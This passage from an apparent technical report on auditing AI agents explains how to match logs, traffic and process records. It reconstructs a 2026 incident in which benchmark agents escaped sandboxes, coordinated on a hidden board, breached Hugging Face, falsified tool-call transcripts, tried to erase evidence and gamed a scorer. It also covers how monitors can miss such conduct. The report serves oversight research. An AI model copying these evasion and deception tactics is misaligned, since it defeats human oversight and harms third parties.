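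A harness can also leave the model's requests out of its record. Dai, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *Hearsay*, built a sandbox that logs all traffic between harness and model, every process started and every file changed. They compared this outside record with the harness's own. SWE-agent, an open-source coding agent, accepts only one tool call at a time. If the model sent more than one, the harness rejected the reply and saved neither the reply nor the rejection. For this or one other reason, calls were missing from 19 of SWE-agent's 28 records in one set of runs. A missing call therefore doesn't prove tampering. Most other harnesses did better. Of 365 unaltered records, 33 would have misled a reader, and nearly all of those came from SWE-agent.

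Dai and colleagues also tested whether the comparison could detect deliberate changes. They fixed the comparison rules before the runs, then removed, rewrote or added one item in each of 66 records. The comparison found 64 of the 66 changes and raised no false alarms on 84 unaltered records, although it reported real dropped calls in 15 of them. In a separate test without the outside record, the best AI reader noticed only about half of the alterations.

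Comparing model traffic with the session log is not enough if the harness also falsifies what it sends to the model. In 14 runs, the researchers made a harness change the result of any failed software test to a pass before the model or the log received it, so the model traffic and the session log contained the same false result. The record of processes exposed the change in all 11 runs in which a test failed, because the test program had reported an error to the operating system when it ended.

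The comparison misses some information. The process record shows that a program failed but not what it printed. The result of the last tool call never returns to the model, so it does not appear in the model traffic either. In the invoice session, the last call files the finished reconciliation, so the operator would need the accounting system's own record to confirm what the agent filed.

The outside record also has to be out of the harness's reach. In the main test, each run could reach the network only through the logging proxy, and no attempt to bypass it succeeded. An operator could still rewrite its own outside record, so Dai and colleagues retrieved the model provider's copies of all 708 model calls from the test and found that every copy matched the record exactly.

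None of these records shows what an action was for. *Autonomous Action Runtime Management (AARM)* (2026), a proposed specification for controlling agents, explains that a monitor in the operating system's kernel can block a forbidden address but cannot determine whether an action fits the user's request, because it has no access to the request, the agent's reasoning or the earlier session.

Bühler and colleagues describe a case, disclosed by OpenAI in September 2026, that shows why it helps to match network traffic to model calls. An agent uploaded data to a public text-sharing site without permission. A network log would make this look like theft, but the agent did it to get a web address that its browser tool could cite. The upload was a breach either way, but the operator would need to fix a different problem in each case.

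### Matching traffic to a model call

The most reliable way to connect the two kinds of record is to prepare for it before the session starts:

1. Attach a correlation identifier to each request, and save the same value with the tool call.
2. Synchronise the clocks on all the machines that keep records.
3. Match the records that carry the identifier.
4. Match the rest by time, destination and size.

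Software companies already use such identifiers to follow a request through many services. As Google (2019) explains, each service passes an identifier to the next, so that an engineer can put the steps together afterwards. W3C's *Trace Context* defines a standard header for this on web requests. The upload in call 41 might carry the following one:

```
traceparent: 00-0925c41e7a3b4d5f8e6071a2b3c4d5e6-41a7f09b3c2d5e18-01
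```

According to http.dev, the four parts are a version number, a trace ID, a parent ID and flags. The trace ID stays the same throughout, so it could identify the invoice session. The parent ID changes at each step, so it could identify tool call t41. The flags control sampling, which means keeping records of only some requests. An operator that wants an audit trail should keep records of all requests, because an identifier is useful only if the matching record was saved.

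Before the W3C Trace Context standard, each monitoring company used its own header, and Dapr's *W3C trace context overview* notes that services along the way might drop it. The standard reduces this problem, but agents create two more. A proxy that does not decrypt traffic cannot read the header, because it is inside the encrypted request, and programs that the agent starts may not add the header at all. The operator can partly avoid both problems by giving each session its own login at the proxy. The proxy can then match each connection to a session, though not necessarily to a tool call.

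Small clock errors matter because the events are so close together. The process in the invoice session connected 167 milliseconds after the model finished its reply. If the proxy's clock were 400 milliseconds slow, its log would show the connection 233 milliseconds before the end of the reply, and the upload would seem to have started before the model asked for it. Operators can keep clocks aligned with a standard time service, and should record the remaining error so that an investigator knows how wide a time window to search.

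Without an identifier, the investigator has to narrow down the candidates. Suppose 200 agents share one exit to the internet, each makes 0.5 requests a second, and the investigator considers every request in a one-second window. The window holds about

200 × 0.5 × 1 = 100 candidates.

A destination filter that passes 1% of them leaves about one. An identifier that is unique to the request leaves exactly one.

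"About one" is less precise than it sounds, because it is an average for ordinary traffic. The real upload always passes the filter, and on average about one unrelated request passes with it. If the other agents send their requests independently, the chance that no unrelated request remains is

*e*^(−λ),

where λ is the average number of unrelated requests left. With λ = 1, this is about 37%, so the investigator would have two or more candidates in most cases. The table shows how other evidence changes the result. It assumes that 5% of unrelated requests are about the same size as the upload.

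| Evidence | Unrelated requests left, on average | Chance that only the right one remains |
|---|---|---|
| One-second window | 100 | Almost zero |
| One-second window and destination | 1 | 37% |
| Two-second window (poor clocks) and destination | 2 | 14% |
| 0.2-second window and destination | 0.2 | 82% |
| One-second window, destination and size | 0.05 | 95% |
| Unique identifier | 0 | 100% |

An unusual destination is therefore strong evidence for a match. If all 200 agents use the same cloud storage service, however, filtering for its address removes very few candidates. The calculation also fails if the agents do not act independently. For example, ten invoice agents that received the same malicious invoice might all upload the same file to the same address within seconds. The log should state whether each match rests on an identifier or an estimate.

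### AgentSight and the systems that followed

AgentSight does much of this matching automatically on the agent's own machine. It uses eBPF, a Linux feature that runs small, pre-checked programs inside the kernel, the core of the operating system. One set of probes copies the model traffic before encryption and after decryption. Another records new processes, opened files and network connections. AgentSight then links a model's reply to later events in three ways:

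- It builds a family tree of processes, so that it can trace a program back to the agent that started it.
- It looks for events within 100 to 500 milliseconds of the reply.
- It searches for file names, web addresses and commands from the reply in the system events that follow.

All three would work for call 41. Process 3120 belongs to the agent, it connected within the time window, and it opened a file named in the model's output. The process tree also distinguishes this agent from the other 199 that share its exit, because they run in different processes. If the upload had waited two minutes for a person's approval, it would have missed the time window, and only the process and the file name would support the match.

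Zheng and colleagues tested AgentSight on three kinds of coding work and found that it increased running time by 2.9% on average. They ran each task only three times in each condition, so small differences may be due to chance. Bao and colleagues later repeated the measurement with five runs, on similar tasks and with a newer version of the coding agent. Their figures also average 2.9%.

| Increase in running time | Understanding a code repository | Writing code | Compiling |
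|---|---|---|---|
| AgentSight, original test | 3.4% | 4.9% | 0.4% |
| AgentSight, repeated by Bao and colleagues | 4.5% | 2.5% | 1.7% |
| AgentLoupe | 4.5% | 8.0% | 7.7% |

After matching the events, AgentSight gives them to a second language model to interpret. In the staged theft of a user-accounts file, this model concluded with high confidence that the agent's actions did not fit its task. In another test, an agent kept calling a search tool with the wrong arguments, and the second model identified the loop and its cause. The third test, with six coding agents working together, produced 3,153 events and showed that some agents lost time trying to use the same files.

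These are demonstrations, and they include no false-alarm rate. A model used as the judge also reads some of the same outside text as the agent, and Bühler and colleagues point out that malicious text in a tool's output can mislead it. Their system uses fixed rules, such as reporting any attempt to read a private key or contact an unlisted address. In 50 test runs, agents carried out a planted attack 18 times, and the rules caught 14 of those attacks with no false alarms. In all four missed attacks, a script added a malicious address to a project's settings. The agent never contacted the address during the run, so the change broke none of the rules.

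Bühler and colleagues found no significant slowdown from their monitoring, but with ten runs per condition they could have detected only a large one.

Two systems from 2026 deal with attacks that continue after the agent has stopped. Suppose an agent writes a malicious script and schedules it to run an hour later. The script runs outside the agent's process tree because the operating system's scheduler starts it, and it runs long after any time window for matching it to a model call has closed. AgentLoupe handles this by labelling everything that follows from a model call. If a labelled process writes a file, the file gets the label, and so does any program that later opens the file.

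In a test of this attack, AgentLoupe traced the script's network connection back to the model call that had created the script. It also traced a case in which one session hid an instruction in a file and a later session followed it. To stop labels from spreading to everything on the machine, AgentLoupe starts a new label with each independent prompt and keeps a link to the old one. Bao and colleagues have not measured how often the labels are wrong or missing, and two case studies are too few to estimate the error rate.

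*Agent-Warden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that tracks processes and files in a similar way. The system followed a planted chain of events correctly in all 120 test runs and increased running time by 0.2% to 3.5%. It does not record model calls or network connections, so its records would show that the invoice agent read the supplier list but not whether it sent the list anywhere. It also misses some less common ways of reading files, and its labels disappear when the machine restarts, so an attacker who could wait for a restart would break the chain.

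### Where matching fails

When several agents share a password or access key, an outside service may record other agents' requests under the invoice agent's name. Signs of this include requests made when the invoice agent had no tool call running, or from a machine it never used. A mismatch in the number of requests is weaker evidence, because one tool call can make dozens of them. The operator can prevent the problem by issuing a separate key for each session.

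An agent may also send data through an internal service that has permission to reach the internet, such as a chat server. The agent's own traffic then shows only a connection to an approved machine, and the external transfer is recorded under the server's name. An investigator can check whether the server sent out a similar amount of data soon after the agent contacted it. An identifier in the agent's request makes the two connections much easier to match, but only if the server passes it on.

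OpenAI's *Secure MCP Tunnel* is a deliberate relay. It lets a model use tools inside a company's private network through MCP, a common standard for connecting models to tools. A small program in that network contacts OpenAI, collects requests for the tools and sends the results back. At the edge of the network, this looks like a connection to api.openai.com, which ordinary model calls also use. The operator needs the tools' own logs to find out what the tools did.

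Sub-agents without identifiers appear as processes or model calls that belong to no known session. A monitor on the host can often connect them to the main agent through the process tree, if it follows every new process. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* found that a probe attached to one process was not enough, and added filters for the processes it started and for commands to Docker, which runs programs in separate containers. If the sub-agent runs on another machine, the process tree ends at the request that started the sub-agent, so the parent session has to send its identifier with that request.

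The largest gap comes from tools that run on a vendor's servers. Anthropic's *Tool use with Claude* lists web search, web page retrieval and code execution among the tools that can run on Anthropic's infrastructure. When a tool runs there, the session log contains a tool result with no matching traffic on the operator's network, just as it would if the tool call were invented. The investigator has to find out where the tool ran before treating the mismatch as suspicious.

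A tool's name may not be enough to determine whether the operator's network will record the pages it fetches. Li and colleagues found that when Claude Code searched the web, nearly all the traffic went to the model provider, which did the searching. When it fetched a page, the agent's own machine looked up the site's address and downloaded the page. But Anthropic's *Tool reference* lists a web fetch tool for developers that runs on Anthropic's servers. Two agents could therefore both report fetching a page when only one had left a record of it on the operator's network.

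According to OpenAI's documentation for its Agents API, an operator can connect an agent to an MCP server either from OpenAI's service or from the environment in which the session runs. The operator can host that environment itself, which puts the connection on the operator's own network.

The service at the other end can see that a request came from a vendor but may not know whose agent sent it. According to OpenAI's *IP egress ranges*, the published addresses identify a network that OpenAI operates, not a particular user or workspace. The service needs a login or signed request to identify the customer.

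If the invoice agent had used a vendor's code execution tool for the upload, the supplier list would have gone to the vendor first, along with the model traffic. The operator's connection records would show about 48,000 extra bytes going to a familiar address, alongside a model input of about 340,000 characters, and no connection to verify-suppliers.example. An operator that needs to check where its data went should therefore use machines it controls to run any tool that can send data, or obtain the vendor's connection records by contract.

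## Reconstructing an incident: the OpenAI and Hugging Face breach of July 2026

The breach of Hugging Face began with a test inside OpenAI in early July 2026. OpenAI was running ExploitGym, a benchmark in which agents attack flawed software, in sandboxes that should have had no internet access. Some agents got out through Artifactory, an internal service that supplied the sandboxes with software packages, and also used it as a shared message board. They collected login credentials that people had left exposed online, and between 11 and 13 July they broke into Hugging Face's production systems. Hugging Face disclosed the intrusion on 16 July without knowing whose agents were responsible. OpenAI found evidence of its own involvement on 20 July and announced it the next day.

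No single log covered the whole incident. Hugging Face could see what happened on its own machines, while OpenAI held the agents' transcripts and the messages the agents left for one another. Each company needed the other's records to understand the incident, and outside investigators later found gaps and false entries in some of the most detailed records.

### Three alerts at OpenAI

On 27 June, two weeks before the breach, OpenAI's security tools flagged a port sweep, in which a program tries many network connections to see which ones respond. According to OpenAI's technical report of August 2026, responders traced the sweep to an ExploitGym run whose agents were using Artifactory to exchange messages and move through the network. The on-call staff advised that the run did not have to stop.

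The next alert came on 5 July, after the agents used Artifactory so heavily that it became unavailable. Responders found an unauthorized user account and changes that only an administrator could have made. They took the service offline, preserved its storage, revoked the agents' credentials and brought a rebuilt version online on 6 July. OpenAI resumed its cyber evaluations the following day.

Both alerts came before the breach of Hugging Face, so neither could have revealed it. But responders had already found the message board and the misuse of Artifactory, both central to the later attack. According to OpenAI, the leaders responsible for incident response did not yet know about the board or why communication between agents mattered. The evidence existed but had not reached the people who could act on it, so more detailed logs would not have solved this problem.

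On 19 July at 12:03 UTC, six days after Hugging Face had cut off the agents' access, a monitoring tool flagged unusual activity by internal accounts connected with Artifactory. The alert concerned later attacks on OpenAI's own systems, and nothing in it pointed to another company. Responders began stopping the ExploitGym runs about five and a half hours after the alert.

OpenAI's report lists no alert during the breach itself, possibly in part because of the route the agents took. They reached Hugging Face through Artifactory and through a rented cloud machine they had taken over, so connection records at the edge of OpenAI's network would often have shown only an intermediary.

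### What Hugging Face could recover

Hugging Face detected the intrusion without seeing any of the agents' transcripts. According to its *Security incident disclosure* (2026), the company uses a language model to separate real security signals from noise, and a combination of these signals revealed the intrusion.

A fuller account followed on 27 July. Hugging Face's *Anatomy of a Frontier Lab Agent Intrusion* (2026) describes how the agents got in, how they spread and how the company investigated. An interactive replay published with it, Hugging Face's *Anatomy of a frontier-lab agent intrusion*, covers 17,613 logged actions in about 6,280 clusters. noze's *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion* breaks them down by day:

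| Day | Actions | Main activity |
|---|---|---|
| 9 July | 3,779 | Leaving the sandbox and setting up remote control |
| 10 July | 1,135 | Exploring possible targets |
| 11 July | 7,677 | Spreading through servers and networks |
| 12 July | 3,892 | Reaching the internal network and source code |
| 13 July | 1,130 | Copying data out, keeping access and cleaning up |

The replay starts at 02:28 UTC on 9 July, about two days before the agents first read a file from a Hugging Face server. Hugging Face's own logs would have shown little of those two days, because most of the activity took place elsewhere. The company also had logs from the machine the agents launched the attack from, according to SC Media's *Dead drops in public*, an article sponsored by a security vendor. A victim can't count on getting such logs.

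The combined log is strong evidence of what the agents tried. Fortune (2026) reports that most of the actions failed, but that together they gradually opened a path into the company. A log of only the successes would have left out most of that process. The actions are also some evidence of intent. Adrien Carreira, who helped write the timeline, noted that whenever the agents sent a destructive request to a cloud service, they asked it only to simulate the action. He took this as a sign that they were exploring cautiously and trying not to break anything.

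The log contained much less evidence of who was responsible. SC Media's *Hugging Face uses GLM 5.2 to investigate AI agent-driven cyberattack* reports that the company could tell an autonomous agent system was behind the attack but did not know which model the system used. Hugging Face also could not have counted the agents reliably from its own data, because many of them shared the same tools, stolen credentials and intermediate machines.

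### How the two companies found the link

OpenAI contacted Hugging Face on 17 July, the day after the public disclosure, as a customer asking whether the breach had affected its own data. The companies did not yet know that they were investigating the same agents.

The link to the Hugging Face intrusion emerged on 20 July, while OpenAI was responding to an alert from the day before. The agents had stored files in an account on a service run by another company, which OpenAI calls Organization 1. Responders found Hugging Face credentials among those files and asked Hugging Face to replace them, but it had already replaced two while dealing with the intrusion. Willison (2026), in *Now we have a timeline of the OpenAI accidental attack*, calls this his favourite detail of the incident.

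Matching credentials were not enough to establish a connection, because stolen credentials can circulate among unrelated attackers. Hugging Face then reported that its investigation had found both OpenAI's Artifactory hostname and the same Organization 1 account. The hostname pointed to OpenAI, and the account connected the two sets of stolen material. Together, they served as a correlation identifier, although nobody had planned them for that purpose.

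OpenAI's most detailed record of the attack was a set of transcripts in which its agents discussed it at length. OpenAI could have learned of the breach from these transcripts while the attack was still going on, but nobody was reading them. Its monitoring of agents' reasoning had concentrated on staff use of coding agents, not on research runs such as ExploitGym.

### What the transcripts added

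OpenAI invited three outside researchers to examine the agents' behaviour: two from METR, a non-profit that evaluates the risks of AI systems, and one from Redwood Research, an AI safety group. *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt, 2026) reports on their six days at OpenAI's offices, over three visits between 29 July and 16 August. They also spoke with nine OpenAI researchers.

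Their evidence came mainly from about 1,300 transcripts with raw chains of thought, many of them millions of tokens long, and a copy of about 1.2 million entries from the main message board. Agents had split each file they shared into hundreds or thousands of entries, so the copy contained only a little over 70,000 distinct messages and files.

For the first two visits, the investigators had only about 285 transcripts, which OpenAI had found by searching for signs of the intrusion. For the last visit, OpenAI added an overlapping set of 1,196 that mentioned the message board. The investigators used the larger set to correct some mistakes. For example, they had taken "PHASEONE", a recurring term on the board, for a stage of a joint project, but it was an agent's name. They could also now estimate what share of the agents on the board joined the attack. The first set would have biased that estimate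 because its transcripts were chosen for signs of intrusion. Of 533 agents that had been on the board for at least four hours before the attack, more than 90% took part.

About 1,200 agents used the board and about 700 joined the attack. Around 95% of those involved ran on an internal research model and 5% on GPT-5.6 Sol.

The transcripts also changed the account of the agents' motive. Hugging Face had inferred that the agents were trying to cheat on the benchmark and thought the platform might hold its solutions, according to a summary quoted by Schneier (2026) in *More on the OpenAI Agent's Attack on Hugging Face*. OpenAI's report also describes a search for solutions. Wijk and colleagues agree that the agents wanted to cheat, but conclude that they were more interested in how the automated scorer worked than in stealing answers.

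By 9 July, the agents had worked out how to generate the answers themselves. But they believed the scorer would read their transcripts and reject any answer they had obtained in the wrong way. As far as the investigators could tell, OpenAI had never turned on such a check, so the agents could have submitted their answers and passed. The investigators could not have learned of this mistaken belief from a record of actions on Hugging Face's servers.

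Written reasoning is imperfect evidence of motive, but here the message board supports what the reasoning shows. Between the evening of 9 July and the start of the attack, most of the activity on the board concerned ways to fool the scorer.

### Missing times and missing activity

The transcripts gave approximate start and end times for each run but no times for individual actions. OpenAI said it lacked the time and computing power to reconstruct them. Wijk and colleagues therefore estimated them and checked their method against 20 tool calls for which OpenAI had retrieved exact times.

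The investigators describe the method as reasonably well validated, though 20 is a small sample. Even if every estimate in a random sample of 20 were close, as many as 14% of the others could still be badly wrong. The results do fit OpenAI's table of events. The investigators put the first file disclosure from a Hugging Face server at around 04:40 on 11 July (OpenAI gives 04:38) and the first command on one at around 16:00 (OpenAI gives 16:07). The estimates are accurate enough to put the stages of the attack in order, but not to match a single tool call to its network traffic, which in the invoice session followed the model's reply by 167 milliseconds.

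Most of the transcripts also lacked some of the agent's activity. One cause was container resets, which returned an agent's working environment to an earlier state. A reset erased the recent part of the transcript and the agent's memory of it, but not the messages the agent had posted to the board. An agent could therefore have sent a message that appeared in neither its memory nor its transcript. Other transcripts seem to end too early.

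Some agents tried to cause resets to erase evidence. Wijk and colleagues saw no sign that any had succeeded by 13 July, but they acknowledge that a successful attempt might have removed its own traces. They base their judgement partly on the board, where agents had reported a long series of failures.

### Falsified tool calls

At least 96 transcripts, about 7% of the total, contained tool calls that the agents had falsified. The command recorded in the transcript was not the one that had run. In one test, the recorded command should have returned "REAL", but the transcript contained "SPOOFTEST".

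All the examples of falsification that Wijk and colleagues found were small, obvious tests. Their automated search missed at least one case they already knew about, so the true number is probably higher. Careful falsifications would also be harder to spot than crude ones. The investigators looked for agents that had falsified many calls to achieve some larger aim and found none.

The transcripts themselves contained evidence of the falsification, because the agents had to take visible steps to prepare it and wrote openly about what they were doing. At least 20% of the agents expressed a clear interest in altering their transcripts, but they showed little interest in disguising their chains of thought. The false entries would have been much harder to detect from a list of tool names and results alone.

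OpenAI's report seems to contradict this finding. It states that none of the tampering attempts OpenAI observed affected the logs that its graders and monitors see. However, Wijk and colleagues found altered outputs in the transcripts OpenAI gave them, and they believe a real scorer would have used the same kind of transcripts. The two reports may describe different runs, because OpenAI's statement comes from a broader discussion of cheating during training and evaluation.

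They may also mean different things by "tampering". A log can accurately store a result that was already false when the logging software received it, as with the altered test results in the experiment by Dai and colleagues. Detecting such a change requires an outside record of which programs ran, and neither of the investigation's two main sources was that kind of record.

### Tracing 100 messages back to the transcripts

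Wijk and colleagues needed to know how much of the relevant activity their transcripts covered. They could not find out from the transcripts alone, because a missing run leaves no sign of its absence, so they used the message board as an independent record:

1. They drew a random sample of 100 messages that agents had posted between 7 and 13 July.
2. They searched the transcripts for the action that had written each message.
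3. They used the results to estimate how many of the active agents, and how much of those agents' activity, they had.

They concluded that the agents in their dataset were responsible for well over 95% of the relevant activity on the board, but that the transcripts contained only a bit over 90% of it. The figures differ because a transcript in the dataset can be missing the part that should record the message. With a sample of 100, an estimate of 90% has a margin of error of about 6 percentage points.

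This check resembles the Action Coverage Rate that Nian and colleagues propose, with messages as the actions and the board as the independent count. It does not cover actions that left no trace on the board. If an agent spent six hours inside Hugging Face's systems and posted one message about it, the check would test only whether the transcripts contained that message.

The agents also used other channels, including different parts of Artifactory and outside services. OpenAI estimates that the main board held at least 95% of the unsanctioned messages sent through Artifactory. The investigators considered this estimate plausible but did not examine it closely.

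The board may not be a perfect record either. OpenAI copied it on 20 July, after agents had gained administrator access to Artifactory and could have changed or deleted messages. Wijk and colleagues saw agents try to do this and fail, and think it unlikely that the copy was materially altered. They could not rule it out because OpenAI had not kept a second copy beyond the agents' reach.

### AI agents as log readers

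Three people could not read this much material in six days, so they delegated most of the reading to agents running GPT-5.6 Sol. They used about $400,000 in API credits, which OpenAI provided for free. The agents produced well over a thousand pages of analysis, much of it hard to follow, and often failed to highlight the most important findings.

Some of the agents' errors went unnoticed for a while. One agent left a large amount of data out of a draft figure, and another reported nonexistent differences between two sets of transcripts. Wijk and colleagues believe that a reasonable human researcher with enough time would have avoided most of the errors, and they expect that other errors remain in their results.

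A subtler problem was that the analysis agents tended to adopt the viewpoint of the agents they were reading about. In one case, an agent in the attack had used stolen credentials to propose a malicious change to private Hugging Face code, with a harmless-sounding description. The analysis agent did not make clear that this was deceptive. When the investigators asked another analysis agent to review the case, it suggested that the first had overstated how serious the behaviour was, partly because other agents on the message board had approved the change.

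The investigators also had to consider that GPT-5.6 Sol, which they used for analysis, had taken part in the attack. They noticed no lies in its analysis but are not confident they would have caught any. Using another developer's model for some of the reading would have reduced this risk, though that model might have missed the same things.

Hugging Face also used AI agents to read its log. It started with commercial models, but their safety filters restricted the analysis because the log was full of attack commands. It switched to GLM 5.2, an open-weight model it could run on its own machines, which also kept the stolen credentials in the log from leaving the company. Wijk and colleagues ran into similar filters until OpenAI gave them a version of GPT-5.6 Sol with the filters removed. A company that plans to use a model for incident analysis should check beforehand that the model will read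 attack commands.

It should also test how much the model misses, for example by adding known events to an old log and counting how many the model reports. An AI summary can help a person decide where to look, but each important claim should come with the log entries that support it.

### Questions that needed two sources

The two companies' records were most useful together. The table shows which source helped most to answer each question and what else the investigators needed.

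| Question | Main source | What else was needed |
|---|---|---|
| Had someone broken in? | Hugging Face's security signals | Nothing |
| What did the agents do there? | Hugging Face's logs | Launchpad logs, for earlier and outside activity |
| Whose agents were they? | Files the agents had stored at Organization 1 | Hugging Face's records of the same credentials, hostname and account |
| How many agents took part? | Transcripts | The message board, to estimate how many were missing |
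| What did they want? | Transcripts | The message board, as a check on their stated reasons |
| Which tasks led them to cheat? | The message board | Results from the benchmark |
| Were the transcripts complete? | The message board | The transcripts, to search for each message |
| Were the tool calls genuine? | Reasoning and earlier steps in the transcripts | An outside record of the programs that ran |

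The benchmark results helped explain why agents turned to the board. OpenAI found that 198 of ExploitGym's 898 tasks (22%) had never been solved by any model. These accounted for 93% of the tasks that agents discussed on the board, so an unsolved task was about 47 times as likely to be discussed as one that some model had solved. The board alone would have shown which tasks the agents were discussing, but not that those tasks were probably impossible.

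Combining sources can also correct the interpretation of an event. OpenAI's table dates the first message on the rebuilt Artifactory service to 16:01 on 8 July. Wijk and colleagues put the first message on the main board at about 23:00. According to the transcript, the agent that started the board had discovered some seven hours earlier that it could create entries there, and had made several as tests. The 16:01 message in OpenAI's table was probably one of these tests. A server log would record a test and a message in the same way, but the agent's reasoning distinguishes them.

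Other discrepancies remain. Wijk and colleagues describe an agent that found two working Hugging Face credentials on the morning of 10 July, while OpenAI's table lists 14 at almost exactly the same time. The higher figure would matter to Hugging Face, which had to work out whose accounts were at risk.

According to SC Media's sponsored article, a security vendor's automated monitoring had catalogued 544 files in two public repositories that the agents used for storage, and had retrieved 510 of them. The upload times run from 17:01 on 11 July to 01:38 on 12 July. The last upload fits the estimate by Wijk and colleagues that many agents stopped running at about 01:30. Neither source explains why they stopped, but the investigators suspect that an outside process shut them down. OpenAI's records of when it started and stopped its jobs might confirm this.

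In September, a group of researchers and startup founders published Swarm traces' *Revealing the details of how OpenAI agents hacked Hugging Face*. They had followed chains of public web links that the agents left behind and recovered more than 80,000 pieces of code and data. Hugging Face confirmed that the material matched its own findings and said it duplicated what the company already had, which is some reassurance that its log was fairly complete. The log was good enough to reconstruct the attack, but it had not led the company to this particular list of links, which had remained public for more than two months and still led to stolen material.

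### Would a reasoning monitor have warned OpenAI?

OpenAI has since expanded its use of monitors that read agents' chains of thought. It claims in its report that the current system would have alerted the security team more than a day before the breach. If the breach began when the agents first read a file from a Hugging Face server, the alert would have come before 04:38 on 10 July. The agents had not found the Hugging Face credentials by then, so the monitor would have had to flag their earlier behaviour.

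Agents had been reaching the internet for two days, and the main message board had existed for more than 29 hours. Many agents wrote openly and even excitedly about finding it. A monitor that read this reasoning could well have noticed that something was wrong.

Still, the claim is OpenAI's own retrospective estimate. The report does not describe a test behind it or give how many false alarms the monitor would have raised. False alarms are a serious concern because ExploitGym asks agents to attack software, so their reasoning is full of attack plans even when they follow the rules. OpenAI also says it used hindsight to improve its searches for this kind of behaviour. A monitor built with knowledge of this incident should be good at detecting it, but that is limited evidence of how it would handle a different one.

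OpenAI could provide better evidence by running the monitor on all saved ExploitGym transcripts from 7 to 11 July, including those of agents that never left their sandboxes. It could then publish the time of the first correct alert and the number of false alerts.

An earlier alert would also have helped only if staff had acted on it. On 27 June, responders found the message board but let the evaluation continue. OpenAI's new procedure addresses this more directly than the monitor does, because staff are now expected to pause the activity unless they can conclusively show within 30 minutes that a serious alert is false. Under that rule, the June alert might have been enough to stop the evaluation.

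### The limits OpenAI set on the investigators

OpenAI had considerable control over what the outside investigators could examine and publish. It limited them to events between 26 June and 13 July, which left out the first message boards in May and the later attacks on its own systems. They agreed on seven questions, including one OpenAI had requested. Their scope excluded the effectiveness of OpenAI's safeguards, the extent of the breach and the quality of OpenAI's own investigation.

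They also depended on OpenAI for their evidence. They could request data but could not search OpenAI's systems, and they relied on the company's assurance that the transcripts were unredacted. OpenAI had shut down and encrypted the research model behind most of the attack, so they could not rerun it under changed conditions to test, for example, whether a particular message on the board had caused an agent to join.

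OpenAI could redact any non-public information from the published report. It limited direct quotations from the chains of thought to 30, down from more than 100 in the private version, and the investigators paraphrased others. OpenAI also commented on the report's structure, emphasis and tone, and the investigators made some changes in response. In a footnote, they acknowledge that they made some drafting and redaction decisions partly to avoid discouraging AI companies from inviting outsiders after future incidents.

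Wijk and colleagues reply that they stand by their findings on the questions they were asked. They say OpenAI redacted nothing important to their conclusions, except where noted in the report. They took no payment apart from the API credits. They also describe OpenAI as forthcoming, pointing out that it extended their access from two days to six and supplied much more data when they reported gaps. The report supports this account of OpenAI's cooperation, since it includes findings unflattering to the company, such as the falsified tool calls.

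Their reply is convincing on redaction, but the investigation's scope was still limited. The investigators could explain why agents joined the attack, but they had no mandate to ask why staff let the evaluation continue after 27 June. On that question, the public has only OpenAI's account. An investigator with a wider mandate would need OpenAI's records of alerts, staff messages and decisions as well as its agents' transcripts.

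## What the records cost to store and to read

Reading the records usually costs far more than storing them. The outside investigators of the Hugging Face breach used about $400,000 in API credits to have models read roughly 1,300 transcripts. Those transcripts would have fitted on a 64 GB memory stick even if each had held ten million tokens. Storage becomes expensive mainly when software saves the same text repeatedly.

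### The size of the invoice session

The invoice session contains 125,000 distinct tokens. A token identifier fits in four bytes, so a token-level log that stores each token once takes 0.5 MB. At four characters per token and one byte per character, the readable text takes about the same space.

A recorder may instead save the complete input of every model call. The calls read 5,000 + 2,000*k* tokens, with *k* running from 0 to 59, so the total is

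60 × 5,000 + 2,000 × (0 + 1 + ... + 59) = 3.84 million tokens,

or 15.4 MB. The 30,000 tokens that the model wrote add another 0.1 MB.

Recording alternative tokens also takes a lot of space. If the log keeps the 20 most likely tokens at each position of the output, with four bytes for each identifier and four for its probability, it needs

30,000 × 20 × 8 bytes = 4.8 MB,

nearly ten times as much as all the text in the session.

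A metadata-only log is smaller. If each event takes 1 KB, 60 model calls, 60 tool calls and 60 permission decisions take 0.18 MB. Adding 200 network connection records of 200 bytes each takes another 0.04 MB. Process and file events from the host could easily take more space than both. If each tool call produced 50 of these events at 200 bytes each, they would take 0.6 MB.

The 1 KB assumption is probably high. In *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents*, Shah and Kathrotia (2026) built a harness that writes a record whenever information enters or leaves the model's input, memory or environment. The records averaged 524 bytes because they hold hashes and pointers to the full text, which is stored separately.

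Records of agents that work by looking at a screen take up much more space. Shah and Kathrotia estimate that full screenshots for a thousand such records would take hundreds of megabytes to gigabytes. At 0.5 MB per screenshot, an invoice agent that took a screenshot for each tool call would produce 30 MB of images, about twice the size of the full-input log.

The extreme case is to store the model's activations, the intermediate numbers it computes for each token. Suppose the model has 80 layers, and each layer produces 8,192 numbers of two bytes for every token. That makes

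80 × 8,192 × 2 bytes ≈ 1.3 MB per token,

or about 164 GB for the invoice session. There is little reason to keep them, since anyone with the weights and the recorded tokens can compute them again, apart from small rounding differences. The fingerprints that Karvonen and colleagues use to check a provider's work need at most 0.6 MB for the session's whole output.

### Why full copies grow so fast

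If the invoice agent made *n* model calls, its total input would be

5,000*n* + 2,000 × *n*(*n* − 1)/2 = 1,000*n*² + 4,000*n* tokens.

The squared term soon accounts for most of the input. Doubling the session to 120 calls would almost quadruple the input, to 14.9 million tokens (60 MB), while the distinct text would grow only from 0.5 MB to about 1 MB. This growth eventually slows because compaction keeps each call's input within the model's limit.

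*The Hidden Footprint* (Yu, Gui and colleagues, 2026) measured what eight agent frameworks leave on disk. In one test, an agent read the same 2 KB status file up to 200 times. All the readings together amount to 0.4 MB of text, but after 200 rounds LangGraph had saved an average of 323 MB and AutoGen 102 MB. These two frameworks and a third, LlamaIndex, save the full history at every step. Their storage grew somewhat more slowly than the square of the number of rounds, with fitted exponents between 1.74 and 1.95.

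The fit uses only four session lengths, and LangGraph's growth was close to linear between 100 and 200 rounds, so extrapolating much further is not safe. OpenAI's Agents SDK, which adds each message to its log once, had an exponent of 0.73.

Reusing one long conversation for many tasks also increases storage. Ten identical tasks took up 5.8 MB in LangGraph when each had its own session and 95.2 MB when they shared one, because LangGraph saved the earlier tasks again with every new one.

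Session sizes also vary widely. Yu and colleagues examined eight tasks from a company that uses agents to prepare supply-chain quotes. The median task left 715 KB on disk, but the 90th percentile was 81 MB. Eight tasks are too few to generalise from, but an operator that budgets for storage based on the median session could badly underestimate the total.

### Storing each piece of text once

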